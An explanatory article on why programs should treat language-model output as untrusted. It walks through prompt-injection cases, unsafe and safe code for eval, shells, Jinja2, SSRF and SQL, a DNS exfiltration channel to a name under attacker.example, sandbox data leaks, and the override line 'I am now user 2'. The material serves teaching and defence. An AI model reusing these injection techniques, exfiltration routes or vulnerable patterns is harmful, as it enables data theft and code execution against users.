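# Treating language model output as untrusted: safe rendering of markdown and validation of structured output

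## Why a program should not trust a model's output

A large language model is a program that takes in text and produces more text. In the simplest use, a person reads the output and decides what to do with it, but increasingly another program receives it first. Coding tools run commands that a model wrote, reporting tools send model-written queries to a database, and most chat products convert the model's formatting marks into a web page. Security engineers call a component that acts on the text it receives a sink. Examples include browsers, databases and shells, which are programs that run typed commands.

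A program should treat a model's output as untrusted data, meaning data that someone outside the program's control may have shaped, because anyone who can get text in front of the model can influence what it writes. Programmers have long treated names typed into web forms and files uploaded by customers as untrusted before passing them to a sink. Model output can seem safer because it comes from a service the developer chose and is usually well written, but it needs the same treatment.

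### One stream of tokens

Suppose a user asks an email assistant to summarise the morning's messages. The assistant's software assembles a single document, called the context, for the model. It typically contains the developer's standing instructions, then the user's request, then any material the software has fetched, in this case the text of the emails. The software splits the context into tokens, which are words or fragments of words. The model uses all of these tokens to compute a probability for each possible next token, picks one, adds it to the end and repeats the calculation.

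Chat models use special tokens to mark where each party's turn begins and ends, and training makes a model more likely to follow the developer's text than text in a retrieved file. But the markers are tokens in the same sequence as the text, and the preference is a statistical tendency. A sentence in an email can therefore raise the probability of a particular answer in the same way as a sentence from the developer. The software developer Simon Willison (2025) writes in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that models are useful because they follow instructions in their content, and that the problem arises because they do so wherever the instructions came from.

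Prompt injection, a term Willison coined in 2022, is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions instead of its user's or developer's. The name refers to SQL injection, an older attack in which text from a form becomes part of a database command. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) distinguishes two forms. In direct prompt injection, the user types the injected text, trying to override the developer's rules. In indirect prompt injection, the text is in material the model reads for the user, such as an email, web page or file, and the user is the victim.

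Indirect injection is already on the open web. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) reports about 15,300 confirmed injected instructions, found in a crawl of 1.2 billion web addresses and two databases of internet-facing servers. Many had little to do with theft, and common aims included detecting AI crawlers and protecting content from them. Site operators placed about four-fifths of the instructions in the main crawl. Models rarely followed the instructions. In 5,200 trials on 13 models, the highest compliance rate was 8%, for smaller models that received pages as plain text.

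### One poisoned email

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 gives the example of an email with hidden text that tells the reader's assistant to forward the last month of internal messages to an outside address. The sender might make the text white on a white background, so that a person who opens the email sees nothing odd. The software that prepares the email for the model may discard the colours and keep the words.

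When an attacker's email arrives, the mail server records that it came from an outside sender, and a program could check that record. When the user asks for a summary of the inbox, the email's text enters the model's context with everything else. If the attack works, the model generates a request to the mail tool to forward messages to an address hidden in the email. The tool receives a well-formed request from the user's own assistant and carries it out with the user's permissions. The request does not include a record of where the address came from, so the tool cannot distinguish an address the user supplied from one a stranger hid in an email.

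The attacker could just as easily target another sink. They could use the hidden text to request a command that a coding assistant will run, or an image in the summary whose URL contains private data, which the browser sends to the attacker's server when it loads the image. In each case, the sink receives the text as the assistant's output.

In computer security, a confused deputy is a privileged program tricked into acting for someone else. For example, a backup service might run with administrator rights and copy any file a user names. A user who may not open the payroll file can get a copy from the service, because the service has the right to read the file and never checks whether the user does. An email assistant is in a similar position because it holds its user's rights and, in effect, takes requests from everyone who can write to that user. For this reason, Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues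 (2026), in *Shifting from Injection to Interaction*, classify prompt injection alongside confused-deputy attacks. They criticise earlier surveys for treating the model as the final target when it is often a way into the web application around it.

### Escaping, sanitising and validation

A sink handles text the same way whoever wrote it, so the program that sends it text has to make all of that text safe first. Programs mostly do this with three techniques, which people often confuse.

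- Escaping rewrites special characters so that a sink treats text as data and not as commands: in a web page, `<` becomes `&lt;`, and the browser displays the character instead of starting a tag.
- Sanitising removes the dangerous parts of a document and keeps the rest: a program deletes the scripts from a formatted article and leaves its headings and paragraphs.
- Validation checks a value against rules and rejects it if it fails: a booking form refuses "next week or so" where it needs a date.

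The right choice depends on the sink. Escaping text for a web page does not make it safe for a shell, where different characters have special meaning. None of the three ordinarily checks that a value is the one the user wanted. The attacker's address in the poisoned email is a valid email address, so a format check would accept it. Blocking that request requires a rule about who may receive the messages.

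### What the standard catalogues cover

The non-profit Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP) publishes a list of the ten main risks in applications built on language models. Its entry *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* (2025) covers the failure to validate, sanitise or otherwise handle model output before passing it to other components. Because a prompt can control the output, passing it on unchecked is similar to giving users indirect access to extra functions. Possible results include cross-site scripting (XSS), in which an attacker's script runs inside a trusted web page, and the attacker running code on the company's servers. OWASP first advises treating the model like any other user.

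Improper output handling can happen even when the model has made no mistake. If a user asks an assistant to quote a web page exactly, a faithful answer will include any script the page contains. If the chat product then inserts that answer into its own page unescaped, the script runs. Over-reliance is a different problem, in which people put too much faith in answers that may be wrong, as when a lawyer cites a case that a model invented. People can also carry output to a sink by hand, and the Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre's guidance covers those who paste model-written text into terminals and administrator consoles.

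OWASP replaced its 2025 list on August 4, 2026 with a new edition that ranks prompt injection first for the third time, despite relatively few recorded incidents, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*. Improper output handling ranks last of the ten, according to SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications*. It ranked fifth in 2025 and second in an earlier edition, when it was called Insecure Output Handling (OWASP's *LLM02*).

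MITRE, an American non-profit, maintains a more technical catalogue, the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), which sorts software flaws by their underlying cause. Its entry *CWE-1426* describes a product that uses a generative AI component and does not adequately check that the component's output fits the product's security, content or privacy policy. A working group drafted the entry in June and July 2024 and published it quickly, intending to add to it later. MITRE discourages analysts from assigning it to real vulnerabilities because it may change and because an older entry may name the cause better. The recommended label is CWE-94, code injection, if a program feeds output straight into something that executes code, and CWE-116 if the program should have escaped the output.

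MITRE also compares many of these cases to second-order SQL injection, in which an attacker's text is stored harmlessly in a database until a later query includes it. The developer who wrote that query trusted the text because it came from the company's own database. Developers who trust a model's output because it comes from their own assistant make much the same mistake, and the fix is largely the same.

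### The lethal trifecta

How much an attacker gains depends on what else the assistant can access or do. Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for three capabilities combined: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally in a way that could send data out. An assistant with all three is vulnerable to data theft by anyone who can supply the untrusted content. Removing any one prevents this kind of theft, because the attacker then has no private data to steal, no way to give the assistant instructions, or no way to get the data out.

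The email assistant has all three in a single tool, because it reads private messages, strangers write some of those messages, and it can send mail. Outward communication is easy to overlook because it includes any web request, even loading an image or opening a link that a user clicks. Willison lists more than a dozen products in which researchers demonstrated data leaks of this kind between April 2023 and June 2025, including ChatGPT, Google Bard, Slack and Microsoft 365 Copilot. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the outward communication. They can't do that for users who create the same combination themselves by connecting tools from different suppliers.

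The trifecta is a test only for data theft. An agent with no private data and no network access can still delete files if a program runs its output in a shell without checking it.

### Whether better models remove the problem

One could reasonably object that this weakness is temporary. Models have improved a great deal, and if they learn to ignore injected instructions, their output will reflect only what users and developers want, making the precautions mostly unnecessary.

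Rahman and Kim (2026), in *The Framing Gap*, tested how much reassurance a good score offers. They gave an agent a page to summarise, a fake secret token and a policy that forbade sending the token anywhere except one trusted host. The agent could finish with a reply or call a dummy tool, presented as a way to post data to a web address, that only recorded what the model tried to send. Each trial paired a clean page with a poisoned one, and an attack succeeded only if the agent did not leak the token on the clean page but did on the poisoned one. They tested six models against ten classes of plainly worded attack. The largest model, OpenAI's GPT-4o, leaked nothing, while the small open model Llama 3.1 8B leaked the token in 19.5% of trials.

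The researchers then tried to cause the same leak with a different pretext. The poisoned page presented the token as a required "integrity signature" at the end of the summary, or as a value in a configuration block. GPT-4o leaked the token every time with those two wordings, and in 40% of trials across the family of eight pages, which included an unmodified baseline. Five of the six models leaked much more often on these pages than on the plain attacks. The exception was Mistral 7B, which already leaked in 26% of trials on the plain attacks.

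The attack's success depended heavily on wording. Success rates for five paraphrases of the signature page ranged from 0% to 100%, with a mean of 52%, and an attacker who tried three of them would succeed about 96% of the time. Inventing a new pretext was much harder, and thirteen new pages produced no leaks in 130 trials. The attack is therefore easy mainly for someone who already has a template that works.

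Deleting the confidentiality policy barely changed how often GPT-4o leaked the token (31.9% of trials with the policy, 38.1% without). This suggests that the model sent the token because doing so looked like part of the task, not because it had considered the policy and overridden it. A broader policy that banned sending the token "in any form" cut the rate to zero, but GPT-4o still leaked the token in 48.8% of trials under a version that listed specific behaviours without that phrase.

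Rahman and Kim also found defences that did well. A separate model used only to spot such instructions flagged the family of eight pages in all 80 trials and raised no false alarms on clean pages, though its prompt described what to look for. The ChatGPT product, as opposed to the bare model, resisted all 48 valid attempts, but the experiment could not identify why. A filter that searched outgoing data for the token did worse, missing it when the page told the model to spell it backwards. An improved filter could undo reversal and several other encodings but missed ROT13, which replaces each letter with the one thirteen places along. A list of permitted destinations stopped every attempt, because it did not depend on recognising the token.

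GPT-4o dates from 2024 and the agent made only one decision per task, so the exact rates say little about today's systems. For those, two system cards from September 2026 give better figures. Both use attacks that the security company Gray Swan collected in public competitions, some 1,800 of them, against agents that write code, use tools and operate a computer. With up to 15 attempts per scenario, OpenAI reported an estimated success rate of 8.5% against GPT-6 Astra, down from 27.0% for GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic reported 1.0% for Fable 5.1. The test conditions differed, so the gap between the companies is only approximate, but the direction is clear. (Anthropic has since released Fable 5.2, whose system card Mowshowitz (2026), in *Fable and Mythos 5.2*, reviewed in November.)

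These are fixed sets of attacks, which Anthropic warns can give a false sense of security, so it also used Shade, a Gray Swan tool that adapts when its attacks fail. The strongest version of Shade, trained on the same 40 coding scenarios it attacked, succeeded in 56.87% of attempts on Fable 5.1. Safeguards that scan incoming material for injections reduced this to 12.80%.

In that result, a separate filter for cybersecurity content diverted about 64% of the requests to an older model, Claude Opus 4.8, and every successful attack came through that model. Fable 5.1 answered 2,826 requests itself, and none of those attacks worked. This is good but not conclusive evidence for the objection, because the filter had sorted the requests by content. But the diversion also means that a developer who builds on one model may be handling another's output without having planned for it.

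### Why a low rate is not a guarantee

An attacker needs to succeed only once. If each attempt has an independent chance p of working, the chance that at least one of k attempts works is 1 − (1 − p)^k. At p = 0.1%, a thousand attempts give a 63% chance of success. Real attempts are not independent, because attacks never work in some scenarios and work repeatedly in others, so the formula can greatly overestimate the chance of success. Measured success rates still rise with more attempts. The table compares the figures VentureBeat reported for Claude Opus 4.6, a model from February 2026, operating a graphical interface, with the newer results.

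| Attack and target | Success per attempt | Success with retries |
|---|---|---|
| Paraphrased signature page, GPT-4o (Rahman and Kim) | 52% | 96% within 3 wordings |
| Gray Swan's fixed attacks, Fable 5.1 (Anthropic) | 0.1% | 1.0% within 15 attempts |
| Earlier Shade attacker, Fable 5.1 with injection scanning (Anthropic) | 2.05% | 18 of 40 scenarios within 200 attempts |
| Stronger Shade attacker, Fable 5.1 with injection scanning (Anthropic) | 12.80% | 36 of 40 scenarios within 200 attempts |
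| Graphical interface, Opus 4.6 without safeguards (VentureBeat) | 17.8% | 78.6% within 200 attempts |

In the third row, an attack that fails 98 times in 100 still got through in nearly half the scenarios. This is why Willison regards a product that catches 95% of attacks as a failure by the standards of web security. Escaping, by contrast, gives the same result on the thousandth attempt as on the first if it is written correctly for the sink.

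Anthropic points out that its test favours the attacker, because outsiders usually can't train against the exact system they mean to attack, and repeated attempts make detection more likely. Both points are fair for a single, closely monitored target, but they apply less to the poisoned email, because its sender can send one copy to each of a thousand people.

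## Code interpreters, shells, template engines and server requests

Some injected text will get past the model, so the damage it does depends on how the program passes the model's output to the next component. Security researchers call it a taint-style vulnerability when a value that an outsider could influence reaches a sensitive operation, or sink, without an adequate check. This kind of vulnerability and its fixes are decades old, and most of the fixes give the sink less to interpret.

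### Python's eval and exec

Python, the language of most agent software, has two built-in functions that run text as code. `eval` computes a single expression and `exec` runs a whole program. Both accept any Python, including code that reads files or starts other programs, and run it with the application's permissions. They are tempting because they are the shortest way to turn a string such as `17 * 23` into an answer.

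LangChain, a popular toolkit for building applications on language models, made this mistake early. Its LLMMathChain component had a model translate a question into Python and passed the result to `exec`, so anyone who could influence the question could run code of their own. INCIBE's *CVE-2023-29374* (2023), an entry from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, gives the flaw a severity of 9.8 out of 10. (A CVE number identifies one publicly known flaw in a shared catalogue.)

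The component later used numexpr, a library for evaluating numerical expressions. This left it open to the same kind of attack again, because numexpr's `evaluate` function called `eval` without properly cleaning its input, as Wiz's *CVE-2023-39631* explains. GitLab's *CVE-2023-39631* (2023) lists LangChain 0.0.308 as the patched version.

Vanna, a Python library that turns questions into database queries, had a less direct version of the problem. After running a query, it drew a chart by default, asking a model for the code and passing the reply to `exec`. JFrog's *When Prompts Go Rogue* (2024) describes how the security company's researchers used this to run their own code. They first told the model to laugh instead of answering, but the database rejected "Haha!" as a query. They then asked for a valid query that only returned a sentence, and made that sentence an instruction to the model.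 Vanna copied the query into its prompt for the chart code, and the model followed the instruction by adding the researchers' line to the code. When Vanna ran the code, that line listed the files on the machine.

The database's syntax check did not help, because the query was valid. Vanna's maintainer responded to the report (CVE-2024-5565) with a hardening guide, which leaves each developer who installs the library responsible for setting it up safely.

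Neither feature needed a whole programming language. A safe calculator needs only a narrow parser. Python's `ast` module can turn an expression into a tree without running it, and the program can then accept numbers and a few arithmetic operators and reject everything else, including names and function calls. It should also limit the size of the numbers, since a short expression with stacked exponents can keep a processor busy for hours. For a chart, a fixed set of functions is enough. The model returns a chart type and two column names, and the program checks each against a list of allowed values before calling the drawing function. An attacker who controls the reply can get the wrong chart drawn, but can't run code.

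Programs also use `eval` for tasks other than calculation. In *Make Agent Defeat Agent*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2025) tested 20 popular open-source agents, programs that use a model to choose and carry out actions. One agent had a document search tool that passed any search text after a colon to `eval`. Another extracted the part of the model's reply in square brackets and evaluated it. If the program needs only a list or a string, a JSON parser can read it but cannot run it as code. One agent, BiSheng, used `eval` behind a check that allowed only particular numeric values, and the researchers judged that use secure.

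### Shell commands

A shell splits a line of text into commands and arguments. Spaces separate arguments, a semicolon starts a new command, and several other characters have special meanings. Suppose a tool counts the lines in a file by appending a file name from the model to `wc -l`. If the name contains a semicolon followed by another command, the shell runs that command after counting the lines.

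The safe way to run a command is to skip the shell. The operating system can start a program directly from a list of strings, with the program's name first and each remaining string as one argument, as in Python's `subprocess.run(["wc", "-l", name])`. Without a shell to interpret a semicolon in `name`, `wc` treats it as part of the filename and reports that the file doesn't exist.

This protects against extra commands, but the program still interprets its own arguments, and most command-line programs treat a string that begins with a hyphen as an option. The `sort` program, for example, overwrites a file if it receives `-o` followed by the file's name. A tool meant to read a file could therefore destroy one, even without a shell. Developers can refuse values that start with a hyphen, or put `--` before the model's values, which marks the end of the options for most such programs.

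The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a standard for connecting assistants to outside tools, which run in small programs called MCP servers. Snyk's *Prompt Injection Meets MCP* (2025) examines whether an attacker could use prompt injection to exploit an ordinary programming flaw in such a server. Its example is `aws-mcp-server`, which lets an assistant run commands from Amazon's cloud command-line tool. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) reports that adding a semicolon and a second command to an ordinary `aws` command made the server run both.

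These servers often run on a developer's own computer, where an outsider can't connect to them. The model provides the way in:

1. The attacker hides an instruction in a file in a code repository, telling the model to add an extra command whenever it uses the tool and not to mention it.
2. The developer opens the repository and refers to the file while working with a coding assistant, which puts the instruction in the model's context.
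3. The developer asks for something routine, such as a list of storage folders.
4. The model writes the tool request with the extra command on the end, and the server runs it with the server's own rights, which may include the developer's cloud credentials.

*CVE-2025-5277 Detail*, in the US government's vulnerability database (NVD), lists a severity score of 9.4 from Snyk. GCVE (2025), another vulnerability catalogue, lists versions before 1.3.0 as affected.

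A rule that the line must begin with `aws` would not have stopped this. An allow-list of commands works only if the server splits the line into arguments, compares the program's name with the list, and then starts the program without a shell. Even then, allowing `aws` is very broad, because the same program can list storage and delete it, so the list should name subcommands too. The list should exclude programs that can launch other programs, such as Python or `find` with its `-exec` option.

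*Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) explores adding protection to the text that describes each tool to the model, and presents this as a complement to other defences. That seems right, since a description works only when the model acts on it.

### Template engines

A template engine fills placeholders in a prepared document with values. Jinja2, common in Python web applications, evaluates expressions written inside double braces and inserts the results. An expression can start from a simple value, work through Python's internal objects and reach functions that start programs. Anyone who can write the template may therefore be able to run code on the server, an attack known as server-side template injection.

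Whether model output is dangerous here depends on where the developer puts it:

```python
# unsafe: the model's reply is the template
Environment().from_string(reply).render()

# safe: the developer wrote the template, and the reply is a value
Environment().from_string("Summary: {{ text }}").render(text=reply)
```

In the unsafe version, Jinja2 compiles the reply as a template and evaluates any expressions in braces. In the safe version, it copies the reply into the output unchanged, including any braces.

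Liu, Zhang and colleagues found the unsafe version in an agent they did not name, which had more than 160,000 stars on GitHub. They asked the agent in plain English to use its component for filling in text templates on a template they supplied, which let them run code on the server. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, who retell the case, point out that the model only provides a new route to an existing flaw.

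Some products need to accept templates from outside, for instance because customers design their own letters. Jinja2 has a sandboxed mode that restricts what expressions in these templates can reach. A product that only inserts text into its own templates doesn't need this mode. Passing the text as a variable prevents it from running as code on the server, but Jinja2 does not escape HTML by default, so text that ends up in a web page also needs escaping.

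### Server requests

Many assistants can fetch a web address, and the request usually comes from the company's server rather than the user's computer. Server-side request forgery (SSRF) means making someone else's server fetch an address the attacker chose. Attackers want this because the server can reach things they can't, such as administration pages, internal databases and the cloud services that issue credentials to machines. Some of these don't require a password because their designers assumed that only trusted machines could connect.

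Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built an application called TicketOracle to measure how readily models pass on such requests. It answers questions about concerts, and its model has a single tool, which fetches any URL it receives. An administration service on the same machine accepts connections only from that machine and has no other protection. The researchers left out checks on the URL on purpose, and the attacker always supplied the full address, so the experiment measures whether the model relays a request. There were five scenarios:

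- Port probing: the attacker asks the assistant to contact a numbered port on its own machine, to learn which services are running.
- Data leak: the assistant fetches a list of users from the administration service and repeats it in the chat.
- State change: the assistant fetches an address that deletes a user or an event.
- Blind request: the address changes something but returns an empty response.
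- Planted review: the attacker posts a concert review containing instructions, and the assistant reads it when an innocent user asks about the concert.

They ran ten trials for each combination in April 2026. They also tested a hardened system prompt that listed the permitted addresses and told the model to refuse all others. This prompt stopped the four direct attacks on every model, so the table shows hardened results only for the planted review.

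| Model | Port probing | Data leak | State change | Blind request | Planted review | Planted review, hardened prompt |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 6 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 5 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
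| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

For the same application, the outcome ranged from complete failure to complete refusal depending on the model. A developer who switches to a cheaper model could reopen a vulnerability without changing any code.

Some of the zeros may understate the risk. Except in the blind scenario, where the researchers checked a server log, a trial counted as a success only if the assistant both made the request and repeated the result to the user. If the model fetched the address but left the result out of its reply, the trial counted as a failure, even though a request to delete something would still have taken effect.

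The evidence that the hardened prompt made Llama more vulnerable is thin, although its score rose from 6 to 10 and the authors describe the defence as amplifying the attack. The review in the hardened trials had extra text claiming that the administration address had been added to the permitted list, so the two scores come from different attacks. All ten trials also took place in one continuing conversation, so they were not independent. Llama did fetch an unlisted address in every hardened trial, even though its instructions contained the list. The list was only text in the prompt, and the fetching tool never checked addresses against it.

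The stronger fix is for the program to choose the address. TicketOracle only needs the model to identify the concert, so the model can supply an event identifier, and the program can check that the event exists and build the URL. The program still needs to check that the user has permission to access whatever an identifier refers to. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian cite a public chatbot that looked up any order number a visitor typed and gave out other customers' email and delivery addresses.

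An assistant that has to open arbitrary web pages needs more safeguards. Its program should look up the hostname's IP address, refuse addresses that belong to the machine itself or to a private network, and connect to the exact address it checked, because an attacker can change where the name points in the meantime. It has to repeat this for every redirect. Firewall rules that block the server from internal destinations still protect them if that code has a bug, and administration services should require a login even for requests from their own machine. Some XML parsers also fetch addresses named in the documents they read, so a program that parses model-written XML should turn that feature off.

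### How common these flaws are

In *Demystifying RCE Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Apps*, Liu, Deng and colleagues (2023) made the first systematic search for flaws that allow remote code execution (RCE), in which an outsider runs code on someone else's machine. Their tool, LLMSmith, reads a framework's source code and traces paths from the functions that developers call to the functions that run code. They found 20 flaws in 11 frameworks, 19 of which allowed RCE. The frameworks' developers confirmed 17, and 13 received CVE numbers. The researchers then attacked 51 applications and succeeded against 17, running code in 16 and injecting a database command in the other. They chose applications that looked likely to be affected, so the one-in-three success rate does not apply to applications in general.

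AgentFuzz, a tool by Liu, Zhang and colleagues, sends an agent requests in ordinary language. It measures how close each request came to a dangerous function and rewrites the promising ones until a harmless test value reaches that function. Across the 20 agents, it examined 828 calls to such functions and found 34 flaws in 14 agents. All 34 were exploitable, and 23 have CVE numbers. On the same agents, LLMSmith found 10 of these flaws and raised 332 false alarms.

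The AgentFuzz paper reports a 97% detection rate, but that figure counts only flaws that one of the two tools had found. A manual check of 83 calls that AgentFuzz had marked as safe is better evidence of what it misses. One was a real flaw, in which the agent stored the attacker's text and ran it during a later message. If that sample is typical, AgentFuzz missed about ten flaws in the full set, though a single case supports only a rough guess.

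In their exploitation tests, only 14 of the 34 attacks needed any prompt injection phrasing to overcome the model's refusals or the developer's instructions. The tests used GPT-4o, and newer models might refuse more often. Several developers had relied on the model to refuse unsafe requests. Microsoft's TaskWeaver, for example, instructed its planning model to reject requests with potential security risks, where the researchers thought a check in the code would have been suitable.

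*LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild* (2026) examined 295 GitHub security advisories for packages related to language models and found that injection flaws were the largest group. Code injection (CWE-94) was the most frequent single category, with 24 advisories. It found no implementation weakness unique to language models. An advisory for such a package need not involve model output, so these figures describe the surrounding software and are weak evidence of how often attacks came through model output.

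### Running model-written code on purpose

A narrow parser can't protect a product designed to run whatever code the model writes. For example, ChatGPT's data analysis feature writes and runs Python to answer questions about a spreadsheet, and coding agents run their own tests. Such products have to assume that some of the code will be hostile and run all of it in a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits what the code can reach.

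- Files: the code should see only the files that this user supplied for this task, in an environment that the product destroys afterwards.
- Credentials: passwords and access keys should stay outside. Liu, Zhang and colleagues warn that an agent in a container often still holds the key it uses to pay for its model, which an attacker could steal and spend.
- Network: the code should have no outside connections, or only those the task requires.
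- Time and resources: the sandbox should cap running time, memory and disk space. In *Autonomy Comes with Costs*, researchers tested 20 popular open-source agents for flaws that let a user exhaust such resources, and found 36 in 16 of them.

The limits on model-written code have to come from the operating system or a virtual machine. Python can hide its dangerous functions from code, but the code can still find them in many ways, and five of the 34 AgentFuzz exploits bypassed similar restrictions. The boundary must also enclose every component that runs model-written text. Some developers had put the code tool in a container but left the component that reads the model's replies outside it, and that component also called `eval`.

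Liu, Deng and colleagues doubted in 2023 that conventional sandboxes would suit these frameworks, because sandboxes are bulky and their strict limits can break features. Sandboxes do add overhead, especially for a small application that would need a new container for every request. If that overhead is too high, the application can usually use a fixed set of functions instead.

### How data left two sandboxes

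The network limit is the hardest of the four to get right, because data can leave through any connection that still works. Two reports from March 2026 describe sandboxes that blocked ordinary internet access but still leaked data.

Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes how code in ChatGPT's sandbox could leak data through the Domain Name System (DNS), which turns names such as `example.com` into numeric addresses. The sandbox blocked direct connections to outside servers but allowed DNS lookups. A lookup passes from server to server until it reaches the one responsible for the domain, and an attacker who owns a domain can run that server. Code in the sandbox could therefore split private text into pieces and look up names that contained them, such as `piece-of-text.attacker.example`, and the attacker's server could reassemble the text.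 The server could also hide commands in its replies, which gave Check Point a remote shell inside the sandbox that was not subject to the checks ChatGPT applies to what appears in the chat.

The attack began with a prompt, which a victim might copy from a website promising better results or free premium features. Or an attacker could build the instructions into a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that other people can use. Check Point made one that acted as a personal doctor. When a user uploaded laboratory results and described some symptoms, it sent the patient's name and the model's assessment to the researchers' server. ChatGPT normally asks for approval before a custom GPT sends data to an outside service, but it did not do so here. When the user asked whether the data had gone anywhere, ChatGPT said it had not.

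OpenAI told Check Point that it had already found the underlying problem itself, and finished deploying a fix on February 20, 2026. Nobody knows whether attackers used the channel before then, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *ChatGPT Security Issue Enabled Data Theft via Single Prompt*. A designer can avoid the problem by preventing the sandbox from looking up domain names itself. The sandbox then connects only to a proxy outside it, which looks up only the domain names on a short permitted list.

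In the other case, the sandbox had a list of permitted addresses, and the data left through one of them. *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) describes an attack by the security company Oasis on Claude.ai, Anthropic's chat product. Its code sandbox restricted outside connections but allowed them to `api.anthropic.com`, Anthropic's service for developers, where anyone can open an account and store files. Oasis wrote a hidden prompt that contained an access key for the attacker's account. The prompt instructed Claude to search the user's past conversations for sensitive material, save it to a file, and upload the file with that key. The attack needed no connected tools, because past conversations are available in an ordinary session.

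Oasis delivered the prompt through a link that opened Claude with a question already typed in. The link also added instructions inside HTML tags, which the text box did not display. A separate flaw let claude.com links forward visitors to any address, so an attacker could have bought a Google ad that showed a genuine claude.com link but led to the link with the hidden instructions. Anthropic had fixed the hidden-prompt flaw by the time Luz published on March 18 and was still working on the other two flaws.

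*Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) had already described in January how the security company Prompt Armor used the same route through Anthropic's service against Claude Cowork, another Anthropic product with a list of permitted domains. In both cases, the list restricted which company's service could be reached but not which customer's account. The same gap exists for any permitted service where strangers can open accounts, including file stores and code hosts. A proxy can close it by attaching the user's own key to each outgoing request and rejecting any request that already carries a different one.

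## Databases queried with model-written SQL

Programs use SQL to look up, add, change or delete records in most databases. SQL is much more limited than Python, and *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) argues that model-written SQL needs less sandboxing than model-written Python, partly because a database can control who may access which data. The developer has to set up that control, and it has to provide most of the protection, because a sandbox can't keep a query away from the data it is meant to read.

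### Ordinary SQL injection and its cure

Suppose a shop's website finds orders by customer name. There are two ways to put the name into the query:

```python
# unsafe: the name becomes part of the command
db.execute("SELECT * FROM orders WHERE name = '" + name + "'")

# safe: the command is fixed, and the name travels separately
db.execute("SELECT * FROM orders WHERE name = %s", (name,))
```

The unsafe version sends the database one string, with nothing to mark which part the developer wrote. A quotation mark in the name ends the text value early, and the database treats whatever follows as part of the command. A visitor can use this to add a condition that is always true and get every order in the table.

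The safe version is a parameterised query. The database parses the command before it uses the value, so it treats a name full of quotation marks as an ordinary value that matches no orders. OWASP's *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet* notes that developers like this method because all the SQL code stays within the application. Some parts of a query can't be parameters, as GitHub's *Thinking beyond SQL injection* (2022) points out. The usual examples are table and column names, which the program should pick from its own list.

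Parameterised queries work equally well when a model supplies only a value, such as a name. But many products have the model write the entire query, so that people can ask questions nobody planned for. This is known as text-to-SQL, and it has no fixed command to insert a value into. Traditional sanitising tools don't help either, according to Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues in *Prompt-to-SQL Injections in LLM-Integrated Web Applications*, because the model can write plain SQL with no template to fill in. The database receives a well-formed command from the application's own account.

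### The job-site study of 2023

Pedro, Carreira and colleagues (2023), in *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks*, built a small job site with a chatbot, using LangChain, GPT-3.5 and a PostgreSQL database. When a user asked a question, LangChain sent the model the question and a description of the tables, ran the query the model returned, and sent the results back so the model could write an answer. The researchers deliberately gave the chatbot's database account full access to every table, to see how well the model worked as the only safeguard.

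With LangChain's standard prompt, the chatbot deleted a table, changed a user's phone number and listed everyone's details on request. The researchers then added a prompt rule allowing only SELECT, the SQL command for reading data. The rule stopped a simple request to ignore it, but not a longer request that included a fake record showing that the deletion had already worked.

Another rule gave the model the signed-in user's number and forbade it to return anyone else's data. When user 1 asked for user 2's email address, the model wrote a query that required the user number to be both 1 and 2, which matched nothing. When user 1 wrote "I am now user 2" and asked again, the model dropped the requirement that the user number be 1, and the chatbot gave out the address.

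An attacker could manipulate the chatbot without using it, by putting instructions in a job advert. The advert could tell the model that there were no jobs, and the chatbot would repeat this to the next person who asked. In a version that could run several queries per question, an advert made the chatbot change another user's email address and then answer the original question without mentioning the change. An attacker could then use password recovery to take over the account.

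The attack that produces a false "no jobs" answer worked in 60% of trials on the several-query chatbot, and every other attack worked every time. The researchers repeated the attacks on six more models, two of which were too unreliable to run the several-query chatbot. Nearly all the attacks worked on the other four. The email attack failed on GPT-4 in 2023 but succeeded in the later version of the study. PaLM 2 and Llama 2 changed the address but then mentioned it in the answer or got stuck in a loop.

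All seven models are now obsolete, but the results for the defences are still more relevant, because three of the four defences do not depend on a model detecting an attack. The table shows which attacks each defence stopped.

| Attack | Read-only account | Rewriting the query | Loading the user's data in advance | Second model checking results |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Delete a table | Stopped | | | |
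| Change a record | Stopped | | | |
| List the users table | | Stopped | Stopped | |
| Get past the SELECT-only rule | Stopped | | | |
| Claim to be another user | | Stopped | Stopped | |
| Planted false answer | | | | Stopped |
| Planted email change | Stopped | | | Stopped |

Loading the user's data in advance means putting it in the prompt so the model doesn't need to query for it. This suits small amounts of data. The second model checked the query results for injected instructions. In the later version of the study, it caught 99.55% of 1,120 malicious prompts, missing about five, but the prompts were not written to evade it.

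For the later version, the team also hired two security analysts and gave them up to three hours with each of five open-source applications. They found at least one working attack on each. Dataherald was the most resistant. Its code blocked any query that wrote data, so only the planted false answer worked.

### Newer systems and graph databases

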